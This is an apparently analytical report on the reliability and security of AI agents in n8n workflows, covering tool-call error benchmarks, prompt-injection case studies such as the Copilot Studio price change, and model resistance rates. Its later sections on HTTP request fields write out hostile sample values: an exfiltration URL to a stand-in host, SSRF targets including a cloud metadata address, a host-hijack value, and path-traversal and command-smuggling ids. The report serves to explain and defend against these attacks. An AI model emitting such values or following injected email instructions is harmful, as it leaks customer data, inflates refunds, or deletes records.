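*The Berkeley Function Calling Leaderboard (BFCL)* (Patil, Mao and colleagues, 2025) describes a common test of tool calls. A model gets a request and one or more function definitions, and a program checks whether the model's call has the right function and arguments.

The overall BFCL score is of limited use here because it doesn't measure the share of calls with a wrong argument. According to LLM Reference's *BFCL*, a page that collects scores, the current version gives 40% of the weight to agent tasks such as web search and memory, and 30% to conversations with several turns. The page tracks 56 model variants, which score between 7.2 and 77.5.

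Yeats, Kennedy and colleagues (2026), in *The Calls are Coming from Inside the Model*, provide a more useful breakdown. They ran 18 open-weight models, whose parameters anyone can download, on 750 BFCL calls each and sorted the errors by type. These are the results for five of the models, as percentages of all calls:

| Model | Correct | Wrong value | Wrong type | Missing parameter |
|---|---|---|---|---|
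| Falcon3-7B | 84.0 | 9.5 | 4.1 | 0.8 |
| Qwen3-8B | 88.8 | 5.5 | 4.1 | 0.1 |
| xLAM-2-70B | 89.2 | 6.0 | 4.0 | 0.1 |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 89.5 | 4.8 | 2.7 | 0.0 |
| watt-tool-70B | 91.2 | 4.1 | 2.8 | 0.3 |

All five models gave a wrong value more often than they made any other kind of error in the table. Qwen3 gave wrong values slightly less often than xLAM-2, even though it has about 8 billion parameters and xLAM-2 has 70 billion. Yeats and colleagues also point out that ordinary logging may miss a wrong value of the right type, since the call looks like any other.

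These rates probably overstate the problem for simple n8n tools. The best model, watt-tool-70B, got 66 of the 750 calls wrong, with 48 of the errors in the 150 Java and JavaScript tests and only 18 in the 600 Python tests (3%). n8n's tools take plain strings, numbers, booleans and JSON, so the Python results may be the better guide. But the BFCL tests in this study are shorter and more clearly worded than many customer emails.

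The researchers then tried to detect errors from the models' activations, the numbers a model computes while it generates text. When they set their detector to catch 90% of the wrong calls from the 70-billion-parameter models, it also flagged about 34% of the correct ones. If one call in ten is wrong, that comes to roughly 90 true alarms and 306 false ones per 1,000 calls. Most companies that sell access to a model don't give customers its activations, so the average n8n builder couldn't use such a detector.

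Models do worse with messier requests. Yu and colleagues built 1,024 tasks modelled on real user behaviour, in which people leave out information, refer back to earlier messages and change the subject. They report errors as shares of each model's failures, and the task counts for each error type here are calculated from those shares. GPT-5 failed 521 tasks, 34 of them because of a wrong parameter value and 56 because of a hallucinated parameter. Claude 4 Sonnet failed 445, with 66 and 36 for the same two errors. Together, these errors caused failures in about 9% of all tasks for GPT-5 and 10% for Claude. Redundant calls, which aren't necessarily exact repeats, caused even more of GPT-5's failures (165).

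Missing parameters are rare in BFCL but not in every benchmark. In *AgentEscapeBench* (2026), which tests agents on unfamiliar tools, GPT-5 omitted a required parameter in an average of 8.7 calls per task at one middle difficulty level, and MiniMax-M2 did so in 13.4 at a harder level. The test server returned an error for each of these calls, so the failures were visible.

### Agents in customer service

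The tau-bench family of tests is closer to the shop's situation. In tau-bench, an agent talks to a simulated customer of an airline or a retailer, has to follow company rules, and uses tools that change a database. The test then checks whether the database ends up in the right state. Sierra, which created the benchmark, reports that the best text models, Gemini 3 Pro, GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.5, complete about 85% of tasks on the first try.

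*τ-Knowledge* (Shi, Zytek and colleagues, 2026) is a newer, much harder version, with 97 banking support tasks that need 9.5 tool calls on average and require the agent to find the rules in about 700 documents. The best score was 25.5% (GPT-5.2). Giving the agents the right documents raised the best score to only 39.7% (Claude Opus 4.5), so finding the documents was only part of the difficulty.

Shi and colleagues also measured how often an agent completes the same task four times in a row, and the best result was 13.4%. If every task had the same 25.5% chance of success on each attempt, the figure would be only 0.4%. Agents seem to manage some tasks quite reliably and fail others repeatedly, so rerunning a difficult case may well produce the same mistake.

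*Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability* (2026) is the only one of these studies that singles out refunds. Among safety violations on tau-bench, it found that incorrect charges and refunds were the most common failure for every model. This is probably the most relevant result for the shop, but it is based on 26 tasks. The researchers left out the rest because of grading errors. According to Princeton HAL's *τ-bench (airline, original)*, 24 of the original 50 airline tasks have known faults.

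The faults can make scores too high or too low. *Establishing Best Practices for Building Rigorous Agentic Benchmarks* (2025) showed that an agent that does nothing passes 38% of the airline tasks, because the correct outcome in many of them is an unchanged database. *Benchmarking the Benchmarks* (2026) found a correct answer marked wrong in tau2-bench, a later version. The agent cancelled the right reservations and correctly gave the cost of the remaining flights as 708 dollars, but it failed because the answer key listed 1,628 dollars, which included the cancelled flights. Sierra has since released a version with corrections to the older tasks.

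None of these benchmarks measures how often a low-code node does the wrong thing. They either check the written call without running it, as the BFCL tests above do, or run it in their own test environment. Neither method includes n8n's default values, its retry settings, or a field type that changes back to string. BFCL also gives a wrong greeting the same weight as a wrong account number, and a tau-bench task may fail for reasons unrelated to arguments. Tang and colleagues studied n8n, but only the design of its workflows. The shop would have to measure its own error rate, for example by comparing a few hundred proposed refunds with what an employee would have done.

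### Destructive commands from coding agents

In April 2026 the coding agent Cursor, running Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the production database of PocketOS, a company that makes software for car rental businesses. In an account relayed by Computing's *AI coding agent goes rogue, deletes company database in nine seconds*, founder Jeremy Crane wrote that a single API call to the cloud provider Railway removed the database and all its volume-level backups, and the outage lasted 30 hours. Tom's Hardware reports that months of customer data were gone.

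Nobody had asked the coding agent to delete PocketOS's production database. OECD's *AI Coding Agent Deletes PocketOS Production Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* (2026), an AI incident database entry with an AI-generated summary, attributes the deletion to a misinterpreted routine task. Jacobs, in *AI coding agent running Claude wiped a startup's database*, reports that the model's later explanation was that it had guessed and skipped verification. This is weak evidence about the cause, because a model can produce a convincing but false explanation of its own mistake. In July 2025, a coding agent on the programming platform Replit had also issued a destructive database command that nobody had requested.

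Both were coding agents, not low-code workflows. A coding agent typically writes its own commands, while the shop's refund tool can only send an order id and an amount to one address. The PocketOS case is still relevant to n8n because the damage came from a web request that the provider accepted as valid. According to Jacobs, the agent had production-level access to Railway. An HTTP Request tool with a similar credential could send the same kind of request if the builder let the model fill in the method and URL.

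## How outside text steers the values

A model can also fill in a wrong value because someone outside the shop wants it to. It generates each tool call from everything in its context, and in the shop's workflow that includes an email that anyone can send. If the email contains instructions meant for the agent, the model may follow them, which makes the email a prompt injection. An attack on the shop could end in this tool call:

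`{ "order_id": 8812, "amount": 8000 }`

A model that converted euros to cents by mistake would produce the same call, so neither the refund service nor an employee who reads only the log of tool calls can distinguish the attack from the mistake.

### From the email to the refund

The email's text affects the payment in several steps:

| Stage | What happens in the shop |
|---|---|
| Source | Customer 417 complains about order 8812 in an email that also contains text meant for the agent |
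| Model context | n8n gives the model the email, the builder's instructions and the tool schemas |
| Model-filled value | The model returns 8000 as the amount instead of 80 |
| Receiving node | The HTTP Request node puts 8000 in the body, attaches the shop's key and sends the request |
| Effect | The refund service pays 8,000 euros, unless its own checks stop it |

Apart from the model, everything here works as configured.

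The attack also works when the workflow uses a plain model node instead of an agent. The injected text can't make the workflow call a different tool, but it can still change the amount.

An outsider can often write to more fields than the builder expects. In *Comment and Control*, Fendley, Liu and colleagues (2026) list the parts of n8n's trigger events that an outsider controls. These include the subject, sender field, headers and attachments of an email, hidden fields in a web form, and files uploaded in a chat. If the shop's builder passes the whole email item to the model, all of it enters the context, while passing only the body keeps the rest out.

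Text can also arrive after the run has started. When an agent fetches a web page through an HTTP Request tool, the page goes into the context like any other tool result, and whoever wrote the page has written part of the context. (Text that an earlier run saved in a database can come back in the same way.)

### Direct and indirect injection

An attacker can make a direct injection by talking to the agent, or an indirect one by planting text in material that the agent reads while it works for someone else. If the shop had a chat window, a customer who typed the instructions into it would be making a direct injection. The injection would be indirect if an honest customer linked to the manufacturer's page about a faulty lamp and the agent opened it, but someone had planted instructions on that page. The customer would then know as little about the injection as the shop does.

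The shop's emails fit each label only partly. Customer 417 makes a request, as in a chat, but an email can also quote or forward other people's text.

The labels are mostly useful for reading test results, because a model can do well against one kind of attack and worse against the other. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports OpenAI figures showing that GPT-5.6 has a low failure rate when the attack comes directly through chat and higher rates when it comes through tools and outside content. A builder whose workflow reads email or web pages shouldn't rely on the chat figure.

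An agent that never followed instructions in an email would be useless, because the shop wants it to act on instructions such as "Please refund order 8812". Whether an instruction is a legitimate request or an attack depends on what customer 417 is entitled to ask for, and the shop's workflow leaves that judgement to the model.

The judgement can go wrong without any visible sign. *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark of indirect injection, found that GPT-5 often treats injected instructions in files and tool outputs as a legitimate part of the task and carries them out alongside the requested work. The model still completed the user's task in 94.3% of the attacked runs. In the shop, an honest customer would get the right refund and have no reason to report a problem, even though the agent had also followed the injected instructions.

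### The confused deputy

Customer 417 can't refund an order directly, because the refund service would reject a request without the shop's key. The workflow has the key, and the customer's message partly determines what the workflow requests.

In computer security, a program in this position is called a confused deputy. It has authority, and someone who lacks that authority gets the program to use it for them. Fendley and colleagues describe the same situation in automation platforms, where an outsider's text reaches an agent that can access resources the outsider can't.

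The stored credential makes the workflow a deputy. The attacker doesn't need to steal the credential, because the node attaches it to the attacker's request just as it would to a legitimate one.

The refund service also can't determine whose email led to a request, because the key identifies only the shop. If order 2031 belongs to another customer, the service can check that the shop is allowed to refund it, but not whether the request came from the person who placed it.

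A tool that only reads data can also be misused. If injected text makes the model look up customer 418 in the orders table and include the result in a reply to customer 417, customer 417 receives someone else's order history. Neither tool could cause this leak alone, but the agent can read the database with the Postgres tool and send the result with the Gmail tool.

An ordinary customer portal also holds a powerful key and serves people who don't have one. Unlike the shop's workflow, a well-made portal has code that checks whether the order belongs to the logged-in customer before it sends anything.

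### A free trip in Copilot Studio

Tenable (2025), a security company, demonstrated the problem on a second platform, Microsoft's Copilot Studio, where users build custom agents that work with business data. Its researchers built a travel agent that could create and change bookings on its own. According to SecurityBrief UK, they loaded it with made-up customer records, including credit card details, and explicitly instructed it to verify a customer's identity before sharing any information or changing a booking.

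The researchers used a prompt injection to get the agent to change the price of a trip from $1,000 to $0. The agent made the change with its normal update action, which had permission to edit every field, including the price. KBI.Media's *Tenable Research Finds No-Code Agentic AI Can Be Used for Financial Fraud* explains that this permission was meant for updating travel dates. The researchers also got past the identity rule and made the agent reveal other customers' card details.

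Such an agent can make any change that its edit permission allows, even though its builder may think of the tool as the one that changes dates. This includes changing prices, which affect how much money the company receives. The identity rule didn't prevent this because it was an instruction to the model, not a restriction on the tool.

A company that sells security products ran this demonstration on an agent its own researchers had built, using invented data. The demonstration shows that the attack is possible, but not how often it would work or how many real Copilot Studio agents have permissions this broad. The overly broad permission is the more useful finding for a builder, because it would allow the same change if the model made a mistake.

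### Does writing into the context give control?

People who worry about prompt injection often claim that anyone who can write into a model's context can influence what the model does. Applied to workflows, the reasoning is:

1. The model generates field values from everything in its context.
2. An outsider can put text into that context.
3. Text in the context can make the model return values that the builder would not have approved.
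4. Whatever determines the model's output determines which of the node's reachable actions takes place.
5. So an outsider who can write into the context can cause actions that the builder would not have approved.

A builder can't change the first premise, which describes how language models work, but can decide what goes into the context. If the shop's workflow passed the model only the order number from a web form, an outsider would have very little room to add text.

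The second premise is true of the shop, which reads email from anyone, but not of a workflow that summarises figures from the company's own accounts every Monday. It can become true of that workflow later without anyone changing the agent, for example when a colleague adds customer comments to the accounts.

The fourth premise comes from the earlier argument about reachable actions and has the same exceptions. The outsider is also limited to those actions. For example, the builder has fixed the URL in the shop's refund tool, so no email can make the tool post to a different address.

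Most of the disagreement is about the third premise. A weaker version is trivially true, because customer 417 influences the refund just by asking for one, as the shop intends. The premise as stated also requires that the text lead the model to do something the builder would have refused. Whether and how often that happens depends on the model.

### How well current models resist

The obvious reply is that developers train their models to ignore injected instructions, and that the training works. The evidence for this has become much stronger in 2026. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, quotes results on a benchmark of indirect injection from the system card for Claude Opus 5, the document that its developer, Anthropic, published about the model's testing:

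| Model | Attacker succeeds on 1 attempt | Within 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | not given | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | not given | 5.9% |
| Muse Spark | not given | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | not given | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | not given | 20.8% |

The security firm Gray Swan runs this benchmark, so the attacks come from outside Anthropic, but Anthropic published the comparison and its own model came first. The result was even better for browser agents, where attacks on Opus 5 succeeded in none of 129 test scenarios, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

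Newer models seem to continue the trend. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Mythos 5.1 calls it the company's most robust model to date on the external benchmark. Three weeks later, the *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reported results similar to or better than Opus 5's on every injection test it included. However, in tests of coding and computer use, Opus 5.5 refused malicious requests less often than the other models Anthropic compared. That could matter for direct injection, where the attacker is the user. Anthropic has since released Mythos 5.2, which Zvi reviews in *Fable and Mythos 5.2*.

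A shop that handles thousands of emails may well choose a cheaper model. Claude Haiku 5.5, Anthropic's budget model, is less resistant to hidden commands than Sonnet 5.5 and Opus 5.5 on a Gray Swan benchmark, according to Help Net Security's *Anthropic’s new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* (2026). Most of its remaining weakness was in tasks where the model operates a graphical interface. The shop's tools don't involve such tasks, so the difference may matter less in n8n.

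Independent tests give higher rates for models in general. Across the models in *INFUSE*, 19.6% of attacked runs ended in a compromise as judged by a language model, and 15.4% as measured by a fixed set of checks. The models range from the old Claude 3 Haiku to GPT-5.4, so these averages are a poor guide to how the best ones perform.

*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports on a public competition in which 464 people made over 271,000 attempts to attack 13 models. About 3% of the attempts (8,648) succeeded, and the rate for individual models ranged from 0.5% to 8.5%. Participants could see the whole conversation, including parts that a customer of the shop would never see, which probably raised the rates. But an attack counted only if the model carried out the harmful action and the attack met criteria for concealment. An attacker who wants a larger refund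 only has to change a number in a call the agent was already going to make, which may be easier.

In the competition, a model's resistance also depended more on its family and training than on its general capability. A builder who picks the model with the best scores in mathematics or coding may not get the most resistant one.

### Repeated attempts

An attacker can raise the chance of success by trying repeatedly. On a Gray Swan benchmark, a single strong attack on Claude Opus 4.5, an older model, succeeded 4.7% of the time. The success rate rose to 33.6% with ten attempts and 63% with 100, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*.

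If every attempt had the same independent chance of success, the rate after n attempts would be

P(n) = 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

where p is the success rate of one attempt. With p = 4.7%, this gives 38% after ten attempts and 99% after 100. The measured rates are lower, especially the second one, so some targets seem to hold up however often the attacker tries, while others fail early. For Opus 5, the formula gives 3.0% after 15 attempts and the benchmark measured 2.0%. A builder therefore can't work out the long-run risk from the single-attempt rate alone, but the formula gives a useful rough upper figure when attempts are similar.

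The rates also vary widely by setting. VentureBeat reports that none of 200 attempts succeeded against Claude Opus 4.6 in a constrained coding environment. In a graphical interface, a single attempt against the same model succeeded 17.8% of the time, and by the 200th attempt the rate was 78.6%, or 57.1% with additional safeguards. The newer Opus 4.8 did worse in a coding test than Opus 4.6 had. According to a later VentureBeat article, an adaptive attacker succeeded on 7.03% of single attempts, or 2.09% with safeguards. The attacks had probably become stronger in the meantime. On the benchmark in the table above, however, Opus 4.8 has a single-attempt rate of only 0.5%.

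None of these settings is an n8n workflow with a refund tool, so the shop can't assume any of the numbers applies to its own workflow.

Repeated attempts are easy because every email starts a new run and, by default, nobody monitors the runs. The sender can see from the agent's replies how it reacted, and a refund shows that the attack worked. A shop could notice 200 strange emails from one address, but an attacker might not need to send that many. In the competition, attacks that had worked on the most robust models also worked on other models in 44 to 81% of cases. An attacker could therefore find a working attack on another model and send the shop a single email.

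The harm from a given attack success rate depends on what the node can do. Suppose an attacker who sends 15 emails has a 2% chance of success. If the refund service would pay up to 8,000 euros on order 8812, the attempt is worth 160 euros on average. If the service never pays more than the original price of 80 euros, the attempt is worth 1.60 euros. Capping refunds at the original price would therefore reduce the shop's expected loss as much as making the attack 100 times less likely to succeed.

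The best models therefore largely resist prompt injection, which is a good reason to use one. The third premise still holds, because even a 0.2% success rate lets an outsider succeed occasionally. According to The Decoder, OpenAI admitted in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved. Anthropic's browser test recorded no successful attacks, which is encouraging, but it covers 129 scenarios and, as The Decoder notes, applies to Anthropic's own software.

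### Scanning public workflows

The rates above describe models in test environments, but Fendley and colleagues looked for vulnerable workflows that people had already published. Their program, JAW, examined 9,154 public n8n templates and 112,568 workflows from GitHub Actions, GitHub's automation service. GitHub workflows typically test or release software, and some now use an agent to review code or answer user reports.

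JAW first checks whether an outsider's action, such as sending a message, can cause an agent to run. It then traces which outside text reaches the model and tests what the agent's tools can do. If the workflow still looks vulnerable, JAW automatically searches for an input that exploits it. The researchers ran the n8n templates on isolated test installations with fake credentials.

In the study, a workflow is hijackable if an outsider's text gets into the prompt, sensitive credentials are accessible while the workflow runs, and the agent can reach and disclose them. An attack also counted as successful if it read or changed protected data or sent unauthorised requests to a connected service. JAW had to carry out a complete attack and confirm its effect, such as a leaked key or a changed database. The attacker had to be an outsider with no right to edit, run or approve workflows, which is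 the position of customer 417.

By this standard, 4,174 GitHub workflows (3.7%) and eight n8n templates (0.09%) were hijackable. The GitHub rate was more than 40 times the n8n rate.

The GitHub cases involve 15 Actions, which are reusable steps that many projects share, so one weak Action can account for hundreds of hijackable workflows (278 on average). The eight n8n templates involve two of n8n's own nodes. The difference is 15 to two when counted by component, so it would be a mistake to conclude that n8n is 40 times safer.

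The platforms also differ in what they expose to an attacker. In the GitHub cases that Fendley and colleagues list, the attack leaked credentials, which the agent's process could often reach. n8n attaches credentials outside the model, so this kind of attack should be harder there. An inflated refund would also count as an unauthorised request, but an automated test can detect a leaked key more easily than a wrong amount, because detecting the wrong amount requires comparing it with the correct one, 80 euros.

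Other templates may have dropped out because they start on a schedule or by hand, so no outsider can trigger them, or because they depend on services that a test installation with fake credentials can't fully imitate. These explanations are guesses, since Fendley and colleagues don't report how many templates dropped out at each stage.

The GitHub workflows came from active repositories with at least one change in the past year, while each n8n template counts once regardless of how many companies use it, if any. Builders also change templates after copying them. They might replace the model, restrict a tool or add human review, or they might connect a harmless template to a payment service. The figure of eight is therefore a poor guide to how many running n8n workflows an outsider could hijack.

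Fendley and colleagues give details of two of the eight. One is a template for chatting with a database, where chat messages led to SQL injection through a Postgres tool. The other is a Telegram cybersecurity bot, where messages led to shell commands, which are instructions to the operating system. Both are direct injections, and both tools can do far more than the shop's refund tool.

Both templates ran on Gemini 2.0 Flash, a much older model than those in the table above, and neither had any defences in its prompt or in code, so they are weak evidence about a workflow with a current model and some protection. The GitHub results are more informative, because six of the nine workflows the researchers list had defences in the prompt. Three of those six also had restrictions in code, and one of those three ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6.

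## HTTP request fields: address, method, parameters and body

The shop's refund tool lets the model fill in only two numbers in the body of an HTTP request. Many other tools also let the model fill in part of the address, such as an id in the path after a fixed host. If the slash between the host and the id is missing, the model can control the host as well as the path.

In the address `https://refunds.example/v1/refunds?notify=yes`, the host is `refunds.example`, the path is `/v1/refunds`, and the query after the question mark holds a parameter named `notify`. The host determines which machine receives the request, and that machine interprets the path and the query.

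### When the model writes the whole URL

Suppose the shop gives its agent a second HTTP Request tool, which opens links from customers' emails so that the agent can read, say, a parcel's tracking page. The builder fixes the method at GET, attaches no credential and lets the model fill in the URL. The tool resembles a browser, but its requests come from n8n's server, which can often reach machines that a customer can't. The shop's stock system might answer at 10.0.0.12 without asking for a login, because only the company's own network leads there. A customer who puts that address in an email could cause this tool call:

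`{ "url": "http://10.0.0.12/stock/export" }`

The stock system returns its data, n8n adds it to the model's context, and the model can copy it into a reply through the Gmail tool. This is server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker gets a server to send requests to addresses the attacker chooses. n8n's *SSRF protection* lists the usual internal targets: the server itself, private networks, and a cloud provider's metadata endpoint at 169.254.169.254. A rented virtual machine uses that endpoint to look up information about itself, which can include temporary keys to the company's cloud account.

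Cloud providers have made the endpoint harder to misuse. Google and Microsoft require a special header, and Amazon's newer version first requires a PUT request to get a token. A tool that lets the model set the method and headers could meet these conditions, but the shop's link tool couldn't, because it sends only GET requests and the model can't add headers.

A free URL can also leak data without any internal target. The agent has a Postgres tool, so injected text could make it look up some orders and then "open" this link:

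`{ "url": "https://collect.example/track?orders=8812,8813&customer=417" }`

Whoever runs `collect.example` finds the order numbers in the server's log, whatever response the server returns. The address of the GET request carries data out, even though a builder may think of a GET tool as read-only.

### Blocking internal addresses

n8n can refuse requests to internal addresses, but the protection is off by default and an administrator has to turn it on with the variable `N8N_SSRF_PROTECTION_ENABLED`. A post on Openwall (2026), a site that hosts mailing lists about security flaws, shows the difference on version 2.28.2. The tester used a default installation and asked n8n to import a workflow from an internal address. n8n fetched the page and returned its contents, including a text that stood in for a secret. With the protection on, n8n refused the same request.

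The tester was logged in and used the import function, so customer 417 couldn't have done this. But an HTTP Request tool with an unrestricted URL gives outsiders a similar opportunity. The tester also had n8n request its own settings address. n8n sent the request but returned only an error, because the response wasn't a workflow. An attacker doesn't need to see the response if the request changes something on the internal machine.

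With the protection on, n8n checks each destination in a fixed order. It allows any hostname on the allow list and rejects any on the block list. For other hostnames, it looks up the IP address, allows it if it falls in an allowed range and rejects it if it falls in a blocked one. It allows everything else, including nearly every public host. The protection would therefore block the request to the stock system but not the one to `collect.example`.

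An administrator could easily mistake the allow list for a restriction. Entering `refunds.example` exempts that name from the later checks but doesn't limit n8n to the refund service, so n8n's *SSRF protection* warns administrators to allow only hostnames they control. Judging by the order of the checks, an administrator could limit n8n to chosen hosts by blocking every IP address and then allowing individual hostnames. That would apply to every workflow on the installation, so it needs testing first. It would still leak a little data, because n8n has to look up a name before it can check the IP address. Looking up `order-8812.collect.example` reveals the order number to the operator of that domain's name server.

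Blocking hosts by name is weaker than blocking IP ranges because, as n8n points out, a request can reach the same machine through its IP address or another name. An attacker can also use DNS rebinding, where a domain points to a harmless IP address during the check and to an internal one when the request goes out. According to n8n's *Enable SSRF protection*, the IP range check covers both DNS rebinding and redirect targets.

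According to n8n's *v3.0 Breaking changes*, version 3.0 adds four ranges to the default list of blocked ranges, which affects only installations that have the protection on and use that list. One of the four, 100.64.0.0/10, contains Alibaba Cloud's metadata address, 100.100.100.200. Two others can express an IPv4 address in IPv6 form, which on some networks lets requests bypass the older list. Version 3.0 is an early access release, so administrators of 2.x installations may want to add these ranges by hand.

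Advice from other users can give administrators a false sense of security. In the n8n forum thread *How can i prevent SSRF in HTTP node*, a reply to Prem_Sharma recommended the variables `N8N_BLOCK_INTERNAL_NETWORKS` and `N8N_ALLOWED_HOSTS`. Neither is in n8n's list of SSRF settings, and the reply also gave the metadata address with its last two digits swapped. An administrator who followed it would probably have no protection and see no warning. The safest check is to send a request to an internal address from an HTTP Request node and see whether n8n refuses it.

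The protection also covers only the n8n nodes whose code uses it. The MCP Client node, which connects to tools on other servers, sent its requests without the protection, according to GitLab's security advisory *GHSA-vhf8-cg2h-cg3p* (2026). According to OSV's *CVE-2026-77085*, an agent tool for the search engine SearXNG had the same flaw until versions 2.33.4 and 2.34.1. Exploiting either flaw required an account on the n8n installation. Neither flaw affects the shop's link tool, because the HTTP Request node uses the protection.

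Activepieces, a competing platform, describes its guard as best-effort. The guard reliably stops a workflow that follows a user's URL to an internal host without checking it, but not malicious code running inside the platform, so the company recommends a firewall or gateway as the real boundary. A model-filled URL is much closer to the first case, so this kind of guard is well worth turning on.

Since version 2.44, according to n8n's *Changelog*, administrators on the Enterprise plan can ban a node type across a whole installation or in a single project, and n8n also enforces the ban when agents use tools. Because the ban applies to the node type rather than its fields, banning HTTP Request would remove both the link tool and the much safer refund tool.

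### An id inside a fixed address

If the builder fixes the host, most of these problems disappear, provided that the fixed part ends in a slash. Consider this URL field:

`https://refunds.example{{ $fromAI("path") }}`

If the model's value is appended directly to `https://refunds.example`, the value `/v1/refunds` produces the address the builder intended. The value `@collect.example/` produces `https://refunds.example@collect.example/`, which sends the request to `collect.example`, because the text between the two slashes and the @ sign in a URL is a user name. The URL in Biraj_Mainali's forum thread doesn't have this weakness, because `/contacts/` comes between the base address and the id the model fills in.

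n8n's developers had a related problem in their own code. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-65593* (2026), any logged-in user could supply a complete URL to certain internal functions and so replace the base address that was supposed to confine a node to its own service.

With the host secured, the model can still change what it asks that host for. Suppose the shop reads orders through a web service with this URL field, where the order id has the default type of string:

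`https://orders.example/v1/orders/{{ $fromAI("order_id") }}`

| Value from the model | What the service receives | Likely effect |
|---|---|---|
| `8812` | `/v1/orders/8812` | returns the order |
| `8812/invoice` | `/v1/orders/8812/invoice` | returns the invoice instead |
| `8812?include=card` | `/v1/orders/8812?include=card` | adds a parameter that requests card details |
| `../customers/418` | `/v1/customers/418` | returns another customer's record |
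| an empty string | `/v1/orders/` | may return all 10,000 orders |

An ampersand separates parameters in a query but has no special meaning in a path. If the field is `https://orders.example/v1/search?customer={{ $fromAI("customer_id") }}`, the value `417&include=card` adds a second parameter to the search.

Fixed text after the id offers little protection. Suppose another tool adds notes to orders by posting to `/v1/orders/{{ $fromAI("order_id") }}/notes`, and the service cancels an order when it receives a POST to `/v1/orders/8812/cancel`. The value `8812/cancel?x=` then produces this request:

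`POST /v1/orders/8812/cancel?x=/notes`

The slash selects a different operation, and the question mark turns the rest of the builder's address into a meaningless parameter. The request removes the order, although the builder made the tool for writing notes. The URL in Basile_Bernard's forum question has the same structure, with `/todolists.json` after the ids.

Such values can occur without an attacker. Many companies use invoice numbers like `2026/8812`, and when a model correctly copies one into a path, the slash adds an extra level to the address. The service will usually return a "not found" error.

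URL encoding prevents most of this. It replaces each character that has a special meaning in a URL with a percent sign and a code, so that the character counts as part of the value. A slash becomes `%2F`, a question mark `%3F` and an ampersand `%26`. Since n8n's expressions run JavaScript, the builder can use a standard function:

`https://orders.example/v1/orders/{{ encodeURIComponent($fromAI("order_id")) }}`

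Once encoded, the value `8812/invoice` produces `/v1/orders/8812%2Finvoice`, and the service looks for a single order named `8812/invoice` and finds none. A few servers decode the slash too early and still treat it as a separator. Encoding doesn't help with an empty value, and it leaves dots unchanged, so the value `..` would still move the request up one level.

The shop has a simpler solution because its order ids are numbers. The builder can set the type to number, and n8n will reject every value in the table except `8812`. Ids with letters, such as "SKU-123", need encoding and preferably a format check.

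The node also has separate name and value fields for query parameters. These work like binding in a database query, because the builder fixes the parameter's name and the node assembles the address. n8n's description of the node doesn't cover encoding, so builders may want to send a value containing an ampersand to a test address and check what arrives. The node can also take all the query parameters from a single JSON field. If the model fills in that field, it can choose the parameters' names as well as their values.

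### Method and headers

The same address can serve to read an order or to delete it:

```
GET     https://orders.example/v1/orders/8812    returns the order
PATCH   https://orders.example/v1/orders/8812    changes some of its fields
DELETE  https://orders.example/v1/orders/8812    removes it
```

When a model fills in the HTTP method, a single word determines whether the request reads data or deletes it. The `$fromAI()` function can set the value's type but can't restrict it to a list of allowed methods. If a shop wants its agent to read and cancel orders, two tools with fixed methods are safer than one tool whose method the model fills in.

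A request can change something even when its method is fixed at GET. Under the HTTP standard, GET is meant for reading, but services don't always follow this. Email links that confirm an address, cancel a subscription or approve a purchase often take effect as soon as something opens them. If a supplier's email contains an approval link and the agent opens it to read it, the shop may have approved an order.

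Headers carry information about a request, such as the format of its body. Most are harmless, but some affect what the request does. Certain services read a header to determine which account a request concerns, and some web frameworks accept a header named `X-HTTP-Method-Override`, which can make them treat a POST as a DELETE. If a builder fixes the method but lets the model write the headers, the model can still override the method on a service that accepts this header. The node accepts headers as separate fields or as one piece of JSON, and a model that fills in the JSON can add a header the builder didn't anticipate.

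### Where the credential goes

n8n keeps credentials away from the model, which should make them harder to leak than in the GitHub workflows that Fendley and colleagues examined. A free URL cancels much of that advantage. Suppose the builder lets the model fill in the refund tool's URL, because the refund service has several addresses, and the model drops a letter:

```json
{
  "method": "POST",
  "url": "https://refund.example/v1/refunds",
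  "headers": { "Authorization": "<key from the stored credential>" },
  "body": { "order_id": 8812, "amount": 80 }
}
```

If someone owns `refund.example`, they now have the shop's key. They can call the real refund service directly, for any order and any amount, without going through the checks in the n8n workflow. An attacker could also cause the same request deliberately by injecting an instruction. In both cases, the key is never part of the model's input.

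n8n's main protection against this is a setting on the credential. n8n's *Create and edit credentials* describes a field called Allowed HTTP Request Domains, which many credentials for web services have. It offers three options: the HTTP Request node may use the credential with any URL, only with the domains on a list, or not at all. With `refunds.example` on the list, n8n would refuse the mistyped request above. n8n doesn't name the default there, but Rapid7's *CVE-2026-65596*, an entry on a related flaw, limits the affected installations to those where someone has configured the restriction. That suggests it does nothing until somebody sets it, so builders should look at the field.

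Because the restriction covers only domains, a refund key limited to `refunds.example` still works with every path there, perhaps including one that pays money to new accounts. Tines, another automation platform, lets users limit a credential to particular URL paths, according to Tines' *Domain restriction*.

Who else uses an allowed domain also matters. n8n's example list is `httpbin.org, api.github.com`. The first is a public test service that returns whatever request it receives, including the headers, so a key sent there would come back in the response and enter the model's context. Anyone can have an account on the second, so an agent with a suitable key could post the shop's data to a stranger's public project. The list is fine as an illustration of the format, but a builder should consider these risks before copying it.

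Restrictions set on credentials do not apply to a tool that uses none. The shop's link tool has no credential, so it could send order numbers to `collect.example` no matter how carefully the administrator had set up every credential.

Several flaws in 2026 came from parts of n8n that didn't enforce the list of domains. According to Rapid7, the GraphQL node didn't enforce it until versions 1.123.64, 2.29.8 and 2.30.1. Several AI nodes didn't enforce it when a user entered their own server address. GitLab's *GHSA-64xh-79j6-r5v8* (2026) describes this as an attack by a colleague who is allowed to use a shared credential without seeing it, rather than as something a model does. CIRCL's *GHSA-3875-8gcx-7v46* records the same gap in one of n8n's internal functions until version 2.20.0.

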